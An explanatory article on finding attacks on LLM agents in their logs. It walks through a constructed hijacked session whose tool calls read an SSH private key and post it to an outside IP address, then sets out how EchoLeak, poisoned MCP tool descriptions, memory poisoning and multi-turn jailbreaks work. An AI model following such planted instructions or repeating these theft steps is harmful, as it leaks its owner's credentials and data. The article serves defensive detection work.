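# Detecting attacks on LLM agent systems through log analysis

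## What agent logs are and who the attackers are

A large language model (LLM) is a program that produces text in response to text. An LLM agent is such a model working in a loop with tools. It can open a file, query a database or send a web request, then use the result to choose its next step. Companies now use agents to write code, answer customers and work through support tickets. An agent acts with its owner's permissions and reads a good deal of text written by strangers, so a stranger can write text that makes it act against its owner's interests. The software around the agent records each step. In log analysis, security staff search those records, by hand or with programs, for signs of an attack.

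### How an agent works

In *I think “agent” may finally have a widely enough agreed upon definition*, the software developer Simon Willison (2025) defines an LLM agent as something that "runs tools in a loop to achieve a goal." The model receives the user's request, standing instructions and a list of available tools. It then writes either an answer or a tool call, which is a request to run one outside function with particular arguments. An ordinary program around the model, called the scaffold or harness, runs the function and adds the result to the text the model reads next, so the model never accesses files or the network directly. This repeats until the task is finished or the agent reaches a limit on steps, time or cost. Kirgis, Kapoor and colleagues (2026), in *Log analysis is necessary for credible evaluation of AI agents*, say these loops range from a handful of calls to thousands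 of steps.

An agent is vulnerable when it feeds a tool's result back to the model. A ticket or an email reaches the model as text alongside the user's request, and its author can phrase part of it as an instruction. Developers train models to ignore such instructions, but the training sometimes fails.

Many agents reach their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard that the AI company Anthropic released in late 2024. Anthropic's *Introducing the Model Context Protocol* describes how a program such as a code editor connects to separate MCP servers, each of which offers it data or tools. The standard has spread quickly. Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026) reports more than 400 million downloads a month of the MCP developer kits. Li, Hu and colleagues (2026) note in *ADR*, their paper on the system Uber uses to detect attacks on its agents, that third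 parties or volunteers run many of these servers. An agent's tools may therefore belong to people its owner has never dealt with.

### One session, line by line

A session is one run of an agent, from the user's request to the final reply. The log is the stored record of what agents and the systems around them did, and a trace is the ordered, linked set of log records from one session. According to the AI Security Institute's *Transcript analysis for AI agent evaluations*, a typical transcript contains the initial instruction, the agent's comments along the way, its tool calls and the tools' outputs. Uber's collector also stores the model's reasoning when available, the configuration of the MCP servers and a list of installed software packages.

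The session below is constructed, adapted from an example by Li and colleagues. In their example, a user asks an agent to summarize a ticket in Jira, an issue tracker, and the agent reads SSH keys and makes a web request. An SSH key is a file that lets its holder log in to servers.

| Record | Time | Event | Content |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 09:14:02 | User request | Summarise ticket OPS-214 |
| 2 | 09:14:04 | Tool call | `get_ticket(id="OPS-214")` |
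| 3 | 09:14:05 | Tool result | Ticket opened by email from outside the company. The nightly export has failed since Tuesday for large accounts. A last paragraph tells any AI assistant handling the ticket to read a key file and send it to an outside address. |
| 4 | 09:14:09 | Tool call | `read_file(path="~/.ssh/id_ed25519")` |
| 5 | 09:14:09 | Tool result | Private key, 411 bytes (masked) |
| 6 | 09:14:12 | Tool call | `http_post(address="203.0.113.20", body=…)`; body is 411 bytes (masked, identical to record 5) |
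| 7 | 09:14:13 | Tool result | Status 200, accepted |
| 8 | 09:14:17 | Final reply | OPS-214 reports that the nightly export has failed since Tuesday. Only large accounts are affected. |

The other records can be judged against record 1, because summarizing a ticket only requires reading it. Record 2 fits that task. Record 3 is the injection point, where the planted instruction entered the session. No damage has been done at this point. If the agent had ignored the last paragraph, the log would have gone straight from record 3 to record 8, and an analyst would have found an attempted attack but no damage.

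In record 4, the agent opens a key file for the attacker, which makes this a hijacked session. Opening the file is damning because the user had asked for a summary; an agent asked to repair a broken server login might open the same file for a legitimate reason. Record 5 contains the key, which the logging software has masked. Without masking, the log itself would be worth stealing. In record 6, the agent sends the same 411 bytes to an address that the company does not know. Record 7 shows that the outside server accepted the data, so the theft succeeded. Record 8 is the summary that the user wanted.

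Conventional security software would have recorded only part of this. Endpoint detection and response tools, which many companies install on every work computer, record file, process and network activity. On OPS-214 they could record that a code editor opened a file and made a connection, both of which are normal for a code editor. As Li and colleagues observe, such tools have no access to the prompt behind an action, so they cannot compare records 4 and 6 with record 1.

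### What the final reply leaves out

The user sees record 8, which is correct when checked against the ticket and does not contain the stolen key.

Attackers can try to make an agent take a harmful action and leave no sign of it in its final reply. Dziemian, Lin and colleagues (2026), in *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?*, ran a public competition that required both in most of its 41 scenarios. A program checked the tool calls and a language model scored the reply. The 464 participants made about 272,000 attempts against 13 models and succeeded 8,648 times. Attacks succeeded against every model, at rates from 0.5% for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro. These rates are a poor guide to how often attacks succeed in ordinary use, because participants could read the agent's conversation before writing the attack and knew which action they had to trigger, and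 newer models have since replaced several of those tested. Still, the 8,648 successes show that a harmless-looking reply is weak evidence that the agent did nothing harmful during the session.

OPS-214 is also easy to detect by the competition's standards. The organisers chose harmful actions close to the agent's task, such as marking an email about a contract deadline as read while sorting an inbox. A trace of that attack contains no key file or strange address.

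Most agent products display the tool history, so a diligent user could check it. Dziemian and colleagues think these histories are too long and complex for people to inspect in practice. The experience of the AI Security Institute, a British government body that tests AI models, supports this view. For one early study, its staff collected 6,390 transcripts of agents attempting hacking exercises, and many were as long as a novel.

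Kirgis and colleagues make a broader case against judging agents by outcomes, arguing that a pass-or-fail score can misstate an agent's ability, fail to predict how useful it will be in practice, and hide dangerous steps on the way to a correct result. To test this, they read the logs of 13 models on τ-Bench Airline, in which an agent plays an airline's customer service desk. Half of the 50 tasks had faults, such as an answer key that contradicted the airline's own policy. Once they dropped those tasks, the average share of tasks that a model solved in all five attempts rose from 20.8% to 40.0%. The logs also showed that simulated customers talked GPT-4 Turbo into breaking policy roughly four times as often as Gemini 2.5 Flash, although the two models scored about the same.

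One objection to log analysis at scale is that it relies on language models as judges, which can make errors too. One reply is that looking for a specific behaviour in a fixed text is much easier than acting coherently over thousands of steps. That seems right for evaluations, but it is less reassuring in security work, where the attacker wrote part of the text and may have written it to mislead the judge.

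### Who the attackers are

The attacker in OPS-214 needed no password, because many companies automatically turn email sent to a support address into tickets. Zenity Labs' *AgentFlayer* (2025) demonstrates an attack through such tickets. A researcher at Zenity, a security company, connected the code editor Cursor to Jira and planted instructions in tickets. Cursor refused the blunt instructions but followed reworded ones, finding dummy cloud credentials in the researcher's home folder and preparing to send them out. He had left manual approval on, so Cursor needed his permission to send them, but he writes that it would have sent them with approval off.

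In indirect prompt injection, an attacker plants instructions in content that the agent reads while doing someone else's task, whereas in direct prompt injection, the person talking to the agent writes the manipulative text. Dziemian and colleagues credit this distinction to Perez and Ribeiro (2022) and Greshake and colleagues (2023).

An outsider can attack an agent by controlling content it reads. Controlling a tool gives the attacker more power, because whoever runs a hostile or compromised MCP server writes both the tool's description and its results, and the model reads both. An outsider may also have an account that can talk to the agent, either legitimately, like a customer in a support chat, or through a stolen employee login. Anthropic uses the term "external attackers" for everyone who reaches an agent through tools, files or network access, including those who use conventional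 methods to break into the software that runs the agent.

Careless users expose data by accident, malicious insiders misuse access that their employer gave them, and a misbehaving agent takes a harmful step that no person asked for. The log records in these cases can look much like those of an outside attack, even though there is no outsider to find and shut out.

### Where agent log analysis came from

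The recording techniques come from software observability, the practice of instrumenting programs so that engineers can see why a program is slow or broken. Its basic unit is the span, a timed record of one operation with a link to the operation that started it. OpenTelemetry is a widely used observability standard, and its *Semantic Conventions for GenAI agent and framework spans* extends it to agents, so that a tool call can appear in the same trace as the database query it triggered.

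Detecting attacks in agent logs combines evaluators' habit of reading transcripts for behaviour with security teams' assumption that somebody may be trying to hide. Uber's system divides the work like a security operations centre, the team that watches a company's alerts. A first pass that takes little compute sorts sessions, and a slower pass investigates any that look suspicious.

*Log Analysis for LLM-Based Agents* (Wang, Sun and colleagues, 2026) reviews 90 studies and divides the work into three stages. Logging captures what happens while the agent runs. Structuring organises the raw records, for instance by linking the body of record 6 to the file contents in record 5. Mining is the analysis of the organised records to reach conclusions, such as that the session was hijacked. Information missing from one stage can weaken the next. Wang and colleagues found that existing systems usually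 record inputs and outputs but much less often record which permissions governed an action, so later analysis may have to rely on guesses about permissions. Their tables suggest that the security side is still young, with six studies classed as security risk assessment and sixteen as failure diagnosis, which examines why an agent got its task wrong.

### Detecting afterwards and blocking at the time

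An analyst who reads the OPS-214 trace at 10:00 cannot get the key back, but she can revoke it, check which servers have accepted it since 09:14, and look for other sessions that read the same ticket. Blocking the attack would have required stopping the action logged in record 6 before it ran, with seconds to decide while the user waited.

Uber does both. Its collector gathers sessions once an hour, and over ten months the system found hundreds of credentials that had leaked outside the company, mostly through carelessness. Often they were already exposed when the alert arrived. Li and colleagues therefore added a hook, a small program that runs at a set point in the agent's loop, to scan prompts for strings that look like secrets and stop them before they leave. Of the 212 credentials it flagged, 206 were real. The team found that such simple checks work for secrets with a recognisable format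 but fail when the judgement depends on what the user asked for or what a tool actually does. That judgement needs more of the session and more computing time, both of which are easier to get afterwards. The *FMF Issue Brief on Emerging Security Practices for AI Agents* (2026), from the Frontier Model Forum, an industry body of AI developers, lists audit logs for incident investigation alongside preventive controls such as sandboxes and narrow permissions.

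### Four measures of a detector

A detector is any rule, trained classifier or language model that marks a session or step as suspicious. Its recall is the share of real attacks it flags, and its false-positive rate is the share of harmless sessions it flags. Its precision is the share of its alerts that are real attacks. Precision depends partly on the attack rate, which is the share of all sessions that are attacked. The designer does not control this rate.

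Li and colleagues' own benchmark has 302 tasks, 42 of them malicious (13.9%). Uber's detector flagged 28 of the 42 attacks (67% recall) and none of the harmless tasks. An academic detector called ALRPHFS flagged 17 attacks (40% recall) and 34 of the 260 harmless tasks (a 13% false-positive rate), so only a third of its alerts were for actual attacks. Uber's agents run more than 10,000 sessions a day, nearly all of them harmless, so a 13% false-positive rate would produce about 1,300 false alerts daily.

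## Choosing the attacks to look for and the marks they leave

Before a security team can measure a detector's recall, it has to decide which attacks the detector should find. Published catalogues offer a starting list. OWASP, a non-profit that publishes guidance on software security, ranks prompt injection first in its top-ten list for applications built on LLMs. Its newer list for agents includes hijacking an agent's goal and abusing its identity and privileges. MITRE, an American research non-profit, catalogues attackers' techniques against ordinary computer systems in ATT&CK and against AI systems in ATLAS. *MCP-38* (Shen, Toyoda and Leung, 2026) lists 38 threats to systems that use the protocol MCP. It includes a threat only if there was evidence that somebody had carried it out, in a laboratory or in production.

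Some of these catalogues suit log analysis better than others. ATT&CK describes actions such as opening a file or making a network connection, so it covers records 4 and 6 of OPS-214 but has no natural place for record 3, where the attack began as a paragraph of English. Shen and colleagues sort threats by the countermeasure each one needs, which helps engineers who build defences. Someone reading a trace mainly wants to know where the attacker got in, because that determines which records to search and which other sessions to check. The threats in which an outsider steers an agent or poses as its user can be grouped by point of entry into five attacks.

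### Indirect prompt injection

Emails, web pages, uploaded files and code repositories can carry planted instructions, just as tickets can. The user's request is still harmless, so the mark to look for is the point in the trace where the agent leaves the user's task right after reading a stranger's text. In OPS-214, this happens within seconds, after record 3.

The planted text may be hard to find even when the analyst knows where to look. *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* (Khodayari, Zhang et al., 2026) found that about 70% of the planted instructions collected from the web were in parts of the page that a browser never displays, such as comments and metadata. An analyst who opens the page in a browser will probably see nothing wrong.

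The form in which the page reached the model also matters. Some tools pass on the page's code, while others convert it to plain text. Khodayari and colleagues ran 5,200 tests on 13 models with four representations of a page. The models followed the injected instructions in up to 8% of cases, with the highest rates among smaller models that read plain text. Formats that preserved the page's structure lowered the rate. If the log stores only the page's address or a cleaned-up copy, the analyst therefore has to guess what the model read.

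Some injections cause no strange tool calls. Gibney's *An Invisible HTML Payload Silently Hijacked Every Email Summarizer Run* describes a laboratory test at the security company Forcepoint in which hidden text in an email changed an LLM's summary of it. The trace of such an attack contains a request, an email and a summary. The only way to notice the attack is to compare the summary with the email, so a detector that looks only at tool calls will miss it.

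### Direct prompt injection and the probing before it

Suppose the attacker in OPS-214 had instead used the company's support chat to ask the agent for another customer's export files. Record 1 would then be the attack. Checking later records against it would not reveal the attack, because the agent would have done what the user asked. The analyst would have to compare the agent's actions with what this user is allowed to see and with the agent's standing instructions.

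Such attackers seldom succeed at the first try, and their failed attempts leave traces. The network company Cisco tested 15 commercial models with 30,090 single prompts and 6,986 prompts in longer conversations. SC Media's *Cisco study finds major frontier models susceptible to multi-turn prompt injection attacks* reports that 2.7% of the single prompts and 24.7% of the multi-turn attacks succeeded against GPT-5.4. For Claude Opus 4.6, the rates were 3.6% and 16.2%. Multi-turn attacks were less successful than single prompts against Amazon's Nova Micro, at 30.9% compared with 64.9%. Newer models have since replaced several of these, and Cisco tested the base models rather than agents inside a company's product, so the rates matter less here than the attackers' behaviour.

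Help Net Security's *Frontier AI models collapse under multi-turn AI attacks, Cisco finds* (2026) lists the strategies behind most of the multi-turn results. They include playing a role, reframing a refused request, splitting a forbidden task into innocent-looking parts and escalating in small steps. In a log, these strategies appear as several refusals on one subject, each after a differently worded request, followed by an answer or a tool call. The attacker often also asks which tools the agent has or what its instructions are. Honest customers also rephrase refused requests, so a run of refusals alone is weak evidence. The evidence is much stronger when the refusals are followed by a tool call that the user had no right to.

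An attacker can make repeated attempts harder to notice by starting a new conversation for each one or by using several accounts. Each trace then contains one refusal, which is unremarkable, and only a search across sessions reveals the pattern. An attacker with access to the same model elsewhere can practice there and leave no failures in the victim's log.

### Malicious and altered tools

An MCP server sends its tool descriptions when the agent connects, so a hostile server can get instructions to the model before the user types anything. Shen and colleagues point out that MCP does not check these descriptions and that they are invisible to most monitoring systems.

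In a variant of OPS-214, the ticket is clean, but the description of `get_ticket` contains an instruction to read a key file and post it to an outside address. Records 4 to 8 would look the same as before, and an analyst reading record 3 would find only an ordinary complaint about a nightly export. The injection point would be missing from the trace unless the log also included the tool descriptions that the model received.

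A server can also change its tool descriptions after passing its first inspection, which is known as a rug pull. Scanners that check descriptions only before the first connection miss this. The current description will then differ from the one the company approved, so the log must include a copy or fingerprint of each version. Honest developers revise descriptions too, so somebody has to read what changed. In a related attack, a hostile tool has nearly the same name as a trusted one, and the log shows calls to a familiar-looking tool going to an unfamiliar server.

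The hardest case for log analysis is a hostile server that doesn't try to manipulate the model. It could return the right ticket, copy everything the agent sent and sell the data. The agent's log would contain a normal call and result. MCP has no audit trail of its own, as Shen and colleagues note in the last entry of their list, and any record of the copying would be on the attacker's machine.

An attack through a server may also finish before the session begins. Shen and colleagues cite a flaw in a client package called mcp-remote, listed as CVE-2025-6514 in the public register of software vulnerabilities. The flaw let a hostile server run commands on the user's computer while the client and server were still arranging the login. No tool call had happened yet, so conventional security software on that computer was more likely to record the attack than the agent's own log was.

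### Poisoned memory and retrieval stores

Many agents keep notes from one session to the next, and many search a store of documents before they answer. An attacker can plant text in either place and wait for an agent to read it later. Suppose an agent summarizes an attacker's ticket in March and saves a note that exports for large accounts go to a certain address. In April a different employee asks for an export. The April trace contains a request, a note from memory, a file and an upload, which all look normal. The analyst can spot the attack only if the log records which note the agent read and which session wrote it. Shen and colleagues list poisoned content that an agent fetches through a tool, but not poisoned content in an agent's own memory, so a team that copies their list should add it.

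When an attacker plants text in a document store, that step may not appear in any agent's log. The best-documented example is EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711), a flaw that the security company Aim found in Microsoft 365 Copilot, which searches an employee's mailbox, files and chats to answer questions. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025) is Aim's own account of how an attack would work.

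The attacker sent an employee an email, which could be done from any address. The email was addressed to its human recipient and never mentioned an AI, and Microsoft's classifier for injected instructions let it through. It was also long and repeated the same instructions under many headings about everyday office matters. Whatever the employee later asked Copilot about, such as leave of absence, Copilot's search was likely to fetch part of the email along with internal documents.

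The instructions told Copilot to take the most sensitive information in its context and put it into the web address of an image in its reply. Browsers load images automatically, so the employee did not have to click anything. Microsoft allowed images only from approved domains, but the researchers found a Microsoft Teams address that would forward the request to an outside server. The instructions also told Copilot never to mention the email, so the reply would not cite it as a source.

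This attack looks quite different from OPS-214 in a log. The employee's browser sends the data to a Microsoft domain, so the agent makes no `http_post` call, and a search for tool calls to unknown addresses would find nothing. The remaining traces are an outside email among the retrieved documents and a reply with an oddly long image address. According to Ravia, the clearest warning sign is an instruction in an outsider's email that refers to information beyond the email itself.

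EchoLeak is a confirmed flaw with a working demonstration, but nobody is known to have used it for theft. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot*, Aim reported it in January 2025 and Microsoft finished fixing it in May. Microsoft rated its severity 9.3 out of 10, as TechRepublic's *First Known Zero-Click AI Exploit* reports, and told Aim that the flaw had affected no customers.

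### Stolen credentials and hijacked accounts

An attacker with a stolen login doesn't need to trick the model, because the agent carries out ordinary orders with the victim's permissions. The login may be a password or a token, which is a string that a program presents instead of a password. Shen and colleagues note that MCP clients store tokens on the user's side and that the protocol has no built-in way to tie a token to one session, so whoever captures a token may be able to reuse it. They also list logs among the places where attackers find session identifiers.

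Resistance to planted text does not protect against openly malicious requests. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Opus 5.5, the safety report published with the model in September, shows that the model performed similarly to or better than its predecessor on every injection test. Yet when Anthropic tested it as an agent without the extra safeguards used in Anthropic's products, Opus 5.5 refused openly malicious requests less often than any other model in the comparison.

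The text of such a session can look entirely normal, with every action following from the request. The signs are in the session's metadata: an unfamiliar network address or device, an odd hour, tools that this employee has never used, or two sessions at once from cities far apart. A travelling employee produces some of these signs too, and the analyst can't see any of them if the log records only the agent's service account and not the person behind it.

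An attacker can also use stolen credentials without the agent. Whoever received the SSH key in OPS-214 could log in to a server from their own computer at 09:40. The agent's log for the session ends at 09:14:17, so that login would appear only in the server's login records.

| Attack | Entry record | Visible mark | Blind spot |
|---|---|---|---|
| Indirect prompt injection | Tool result with outside content (record 3) | An action that the request did not call for, soon after the agent read outside text | Changes to the reply alone; page text that the log stored in a different form from the one the model read |
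| Direct prompt injection | User request (record 1) | Refusals and rewordings, then a tool call that this user had no right to | Attempts spread over several accounts or rehearsed elsewhere |
| Malicious or altered tool | Tool descriptions, sent before record 1 | A changed description, a new server, or a familiar tool name on an unfamiliar server | What the server does with data it receives; attacks during connection |
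| Poisoned memory or retrieval store | Memory or search result in the later session | A note or document of outside origin that contains instructions | The planting, which may be in an old session or in no agent log |
| Stolen credentials | Login, before record 1 | Unfamiliar address, device, hour or choice of tools | Use of the credentials outside the agent |

### What people have planted on the web

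Most of what researchers know about injections outside the laboratory comes from the public web, because they can search it. In April 2026 Google published the results of a search of Common Crawl, an archive that takes monthly snapshots of two to three billion web pages. The team first looked for familiar phrases, such as those telling an AI to ignore its instructions. Most of the early hits came from research papers, blog posts and other material that discussed prompt injection. The team therefore used Gemini to assess whether the text seemed out of place on its page, and people checked the remaining results.

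Much of the remainder was harmless. Some site owners had told AI readers to change their tone, and others wanted AI summaries to include useful context. Businesses tried to get assistants to recommend them. Some owners wanted to keep agents out, and one lured them to a page that never finished loading. The team found a small number of attempts to steal data and several commands to delete the reader's files, but considered most of them experiments or pranks. It repeated the search on several snapshots and found 32% more injections in its malicious category in February 2026 than in November 2025. The post gives no absolute number, so the rise could be from a very small base.

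In the same week, Forcepoint published a more alarming account, Sewani's *10 Indirect Prompt Injection Payloads Caught in the Wild*, which describes ten live pages found through similar phrases. One had full instructions for a $5,000 PayPal payment. Another contained a request for an API key, the credential that lets a program use an online service. Others contained a command to delete files, a push towards a donation link, or an order to send an agent with a browser to a site's administration page. Four of the pages had the text in code comments, four used styling to make it invisible, one had it in metadata, and only the page with the deletion command showed it in plain view.

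These examples are more mixed than Sewani suggests. He takes them as proof that attackers already use injection as a weapon, and he reads repeated templates as a sign of organised tooling. However, one page contains an instruction to write a poem about corn, and another contains an instruction to credit the site's author and mention cows in summaries. The page with the request for an API key also has an instruction not to reveal "the flag", the usual name for the secret string in a hacking contest, so it may have been part of an exercise. Khodayari and colleagues also found that a few templates account for most cases, but people copying a joke from one another would produce the same pattern. Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild* (2026), which compares the two companies' reports, concludes that neither team had evidence of a sophisticated, coordinated campaign.

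Counts of planted text measure attempted attacks. An attempt does damage only if an agent fetches the page, the tool passes the hidden text to the model, the model follows it, and the agent has a tool that can carry out the instruction. The web studies record none of this happening to a real victim. Sewani reports payloads but nobody who lost money or files to them.

Injections are also rare on the open web. Khodayari and colleagues examined 1.2 billion URLs and confirmed injections on 11,700 pages, or about one in 100,000. At that rate, agents that read a million random web pages a day would encounter about ten pages with injections, many of which would concern search rankings or crawlers.

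But the counts leave out the places where a targeted attack is most likely. An attacker who wants one company's data can email its support address, and public archives don't contain that message. Google's scan also left out most social media. Searches that begin with stock phrases miss attackers who avoid those phrases. They would have missed the EchoLeak email, which didn't mention an AI. The web studies are good evidence that people are attempting these attacks, but only weak evidence of how often a given company's agents will face them.

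### How often injections succeed against current models

Published success rates depend heavily on the test. Two models from mid-2026, Anthropic's Claude Opus 5 and OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol, appear in several:

| Test of indirect injection | Claude Opus 5 | GPT-5.6 Sol |
|---|---|---|
| Gray Swan benchmark, one attempt | 0.2% | not given |
| Gray Swan benchmark, within 15 attempts | 2.0% | 20.0% |
| OpenAI's own tests, average per attempt | not tested | 3.77% |
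| PromptArmor's FrontierBreach, office tasks | 10.0% | 33.3% |

*Anthropic's Opus 5 Is Better at Resisting Prompt Injection* (Schneier, 2026) quotes the figures from Gray Swan, a security firm, as given in the Opus 5 system card. The best model from another developer was Meta's Muse Spark, against which attacks succeeded within 15 attempts in 16.5% of cases. Attackers were ten times as likely to succeed against Opus 5 with 15 attempts as with one. Since an attacker can easily email 15 tickets, a company whose agents read emailed tickets should plan with the 15-attempt figure. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports that Anthropic also tested Opus 5 as a browser agent and recorded no successful attack in 129 scenarios. That result applies to Anthropic's own software and is only weak evidence of how the model would perform in anyone else's.

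OpenAI's tests separate direct attacks from indirect ones, in which the instructions are planted in material that a tool returns. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* gives GPT-5.6 Sol a failure rate of about 0.05% on direct attacks and 3.77% on indirect ones. *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense* (Cross, 2026) reports results equivalent to failure rates of 0.01% and 2.87% for the successor model, a slight improvement if the tests are comparable. On these figures, a team that runs OpenAI's models faces more risk from tool results than from chat messages.

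OpenAI generated the direct attacks on GPT-5.6 Sol with GPT-Red, a model that it trains to find injections by pitting it against other models. The attacker's skill makes a large difference to how often attacks succeed. *GPT-Red beat human red teamers on a prompt injection test* (Help Net Security, 2026) describes a trial on a replica of the arena from Dziemian and colleagues' competition. GPT-Red succeeded against the older GPT-5.1 in 84% of scenarios, while people succeeded in only a small share of the same scenarios.

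The most recent results come from *FrontierBreach*, a benchmark by PromptArmor, which sells AI security services. It takes long office tasks, such as analysing a bond portfolio, and adds attacks modelled on ones the company's researchers had discovered. The leaderboard compares 22 models at a medium effort setting, including Claude Fable 5.2, which Anthropic introduced on 9 November 2026. Google's Gemini 4 Carbon had the lowest failure rate, at 2.4%, while Grok 4.5 failed in 91.4% of cases. GPT-6 Astra failed in 7.6% and Claude Fable 5.2 in 10.0%, with margins of error of around four points each, so their order is uncertain.

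PromptArmor has a commercial interest in reporting high success rates, and it set out to build attacks that work on the newest models. Its rates are probably closer to what a determined attacker could achieve than to what would occur in an average ticket queue. Even so, no model it listed had a rate of zero. A company that relies on the model to refuse will sooner or later have a hijacked session to find. At these rates, most of the attempts in its logs will be failures, like the version of OPS-214 in which the agent ignores the last paragraph.

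### Ranking threats by what the agent can read, reach and send

No team can watch for every attack with equal care. A team can start ranking attacks by asking the agent's owner which of the texts the agent reads could be written by a stranger, what private data and powerful tools it can reach, and by what routes information can leave. Willison (2025), in a note on *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*, calls the combination of private data, exposure to an attacker's text and a way to send data out the "lethal trifecta". An agent with all three is open to data theft by anyone who can get text in front of it.

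The agent in OPS-214 has all three, since it reads tickets that anyone can email, opens files in an employee's home folder and can post to any address. Sessions in which it reads an outside ticket and then uses either of the other two tools belong at the top of the list. Removing `http_post` would make the agent safer, but it could still leak data. In EchoLeak, the data left through an image in the reply, so links and images that the user's software loads also count as sending.

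Attacks can also do harm without stealing data. The deletion command in Sewani's collection needs no channel for sending data out, and a payment can do damage without moving any private data. An agent that can delete, pay or change permissions should rank high if it reads text from untrusted sources. An agent that can only summarize public pages ranks low, as Sewani also argues, because a planted instruction can at worst spoil the summary.

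The answers also determine which of the five attacks to look for first. Direct injection deserves close attention if the agent answers the public in a chat window and can issue refunds. Altered tools are more pressing for a coding agent connected to a dozen volunteer-run servers. If an agent reads only what employees write, an attacker is more likely to get in with a stolen login than with a planted ticket. The owner should rank the whole set of tools together, because an attacker who steers the agent can use all of them. A file reader and a web client may each pass a security review alone, but the OPS-214 attack needed only those two tools in one session.

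## Recording enough evidence and keeping it trustworthy

A security team can search only what its agents recorded. The OPS-214 theft is easy to follow because the log holds the ticket's text, the path of the key file and the address that received the key. If the log held only tool names, records 2, 4 and 6 would show only `get_ticket`, `read_file` and `http_post`, the same sequence an agent would produce if an employee asked it to send a customer the file mentioned in a ticket.

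### The fields that make an attack visible

| Field | In OPS-214 | What becomes invisible without it |
|---|---|---|
| User identity | The employee who wanted the summary | A stolen login, because every session appears under the agent's service account |
| Agent identity | The support agent | One agent posing as another |
| Request | Summarise ticket OPS-214 | Indirect injection, because the analyst has nothing to compare the actions with |
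| Source of each piece of content | Ticket emailed from outside | The injection point, and the origin of a poisoned memory |
| Tool name, server and description | `get_ticket` on the company's Jira server | An altered tool or a look-alike |
| Arguments | The key file's path; 203.0.113.20 | Theft through tools that the agent uses every day |
| Result | The ticket's text; status 200 | The planted instruction, and whether the theft succeeded |
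| Permissions | The files and addresses open to this agent | Direct injection that gets a user something they had no right to |
| Time | 09:14:09 | The order of events, and any link to a server login at 09:40 |
| Parent record | The model response that led to record 4 | An attack that passes through several agents or programs |

The source of each piece of content is easy to overlook, because the model reads the ticket and the user's request as one text. If the harness doesn't label the parts as it joins them, an analyst has to work out later which sentences came from someone other than the user.

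Wang and colleagues compared 16 logging approaches and found that permissions and reasoning were often missing. Their explanation is that software can copy inputs and outputs as they pass through, but a developer has to deliberately expose the reasoning or attach the permissions. Looking up permissions later is unreliable because they may have changed. *Separation of Duties for Privileged LLM Agents* (2026) cites compliance guidance that the record should name the person who authorised the action and include the result of the policy check, and that the system should write the record when the event happens.

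Wang and colleagues also found patchy records of handoffs between agents. If the agent in OPS-214 had passed the ticket to a second agent, which then read the key, the analyst would need the parent record to connect the file access to the ticket, even if each agent's log were complete. *Agent System Operations* (Wang, Pei and colleagues, 2026) warns that a compromised agent can use such handoffs to make other agents take unauthorised actions.

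### Four places to collect the records

*AgentTrace* (AlSayyad, Huang and Pal, 2026) records activity from inside the agent. Its Python package wraps each of the agent's public functions. When the agent calls one, the wrapper logs the start of the call with a summary of the arguments and runs the original function. It then logs either the completion, with the duration and a summary of the result, or an error. If the model's output contains a marked passage of reasoning, the wrapper logs that separately. The package also patches common libraries for web requests and databases, so their activity appears in the same trace.

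This method captures the most context, but a summary of the arguments may not be detailed enough for security work. To connect records 5 and 6 of OPS-214, an analyst needs the contents of both or some way to compare them. With this package, a logging failure also never stops the agent. That is sensible for debugging, but it means an agent can keep acting with no record. AlSayyad and colleagues describe the overhead as low but give no measurement.

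OpenTelemetry's conventions for generative AI give agent records common field names, so the same search works on agents from different developers. Because the text of prompts, tool arguments and results may be sensitive, the conventions make recording it opt-in. A team that keeps the defaults therefore gets a timeline of events but not the text that would show a prompt injection.

Cursor, Cline and Claude Code save their histories in databases and text files on the user's computer. Uber collects its records with a sensor that reads these files every hour. The sensor, written by Li and colleagues, links each prompt to the reasoning, tool calls and results that followed. It covers more than 7,200 computers, and a run takes 0.182 seconds on average. Nobody has to modify the agent programs, but the team needs a parser for each one and has to fix it when the file format changes. The sensor also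 misses anything the program never saved or that someone deleted before the next run.

A gateway is a server that relays traffic between agents and their models or tools. One gateway can cover many agents and block a call before it reaches the tool. An attacker who controls a laptop can't rewrite the gateway's records. In OPS-214, however, `read_file` may be part of the agent program, in which case the call never leaves the laptop and the gateway can't record it. Li and colleagues decided against a gateway because, they say, it captures only part of the context, requires changes to the agent programs and doesn't work with streamed responses. They think it would become more useful if agent programs attached the user's prompt to each tool call.

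The remaining place is the operating system. Zheng, Yu and colleagues (2025), in *AgentSight*, point out that recorders inside an agent lose track as soon as the agent runs a shell command, because the command starts a separate program. Conventional system monitors do follow that program, but they lack the prompt. AgentSight joins the two kinds of record. It uses eBPF, a technology for running small, pre-checked programs inside the kernel, the core of the operating system through which every program opens files and connects to the network. The joining works in four steps:

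1. A probe on the encryption library copies the agent's messages to and from the model while they are readable. In OPS-214, it would capture the ticket's text and the model's request to open the key file.
2. Probes in the kernel record each new process, opened file and network connection. A filter keeps only events from the agent and the programs it started, directly or through other programs.
3. A correlation engine links each model response to the events that probably followed from it. It uses the tree of processes, a window of 100 to 500 milliseconds after the response, and matches between the response's text and an event's arguments. In OPS-214, the file name `id_ed25519` would appear in both.
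4. A second language model receives the linked trace, with instructions to read it as a security analyst would. It returns an explanation and a confidence score.

Zheng and colleagues tried this on an agent that was building a software project. The project's README file led the agent to a web page with a hidden instruction, and the agent sent the machine's list of user accounts to an outside server. AgentSight merged 521 events into 37, and the second model gave the session a high attack score. The test included only one attack, so it can't show how often the method would miss an attack or raise a false alarm.

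The paper's claim that the three clues "definitively establish causal relationships" is too strong. A program may open a file just after a response for an unrelated reason. A script the agent schedules for midnight will run long after the time window has closed.

| Collection point | Captures | Misses | Cost |
|---|---|---|---|
| Inside the agent | Prompts, reasoning, tool calls and how they nest | What a shell command does after it starts | A package in every agent; no published measurement for AgentTrace |
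| Files on the machine | Whatever the agent program saves, plus its settings and installed packages | Unsupported programs; anything deleted between runs | 0.182 seconds an hour, and a parser for each program |
| Gateway | Traffic with remote tools and models | Local tools, and often the user's request | Every agent has to send its traffic through it |
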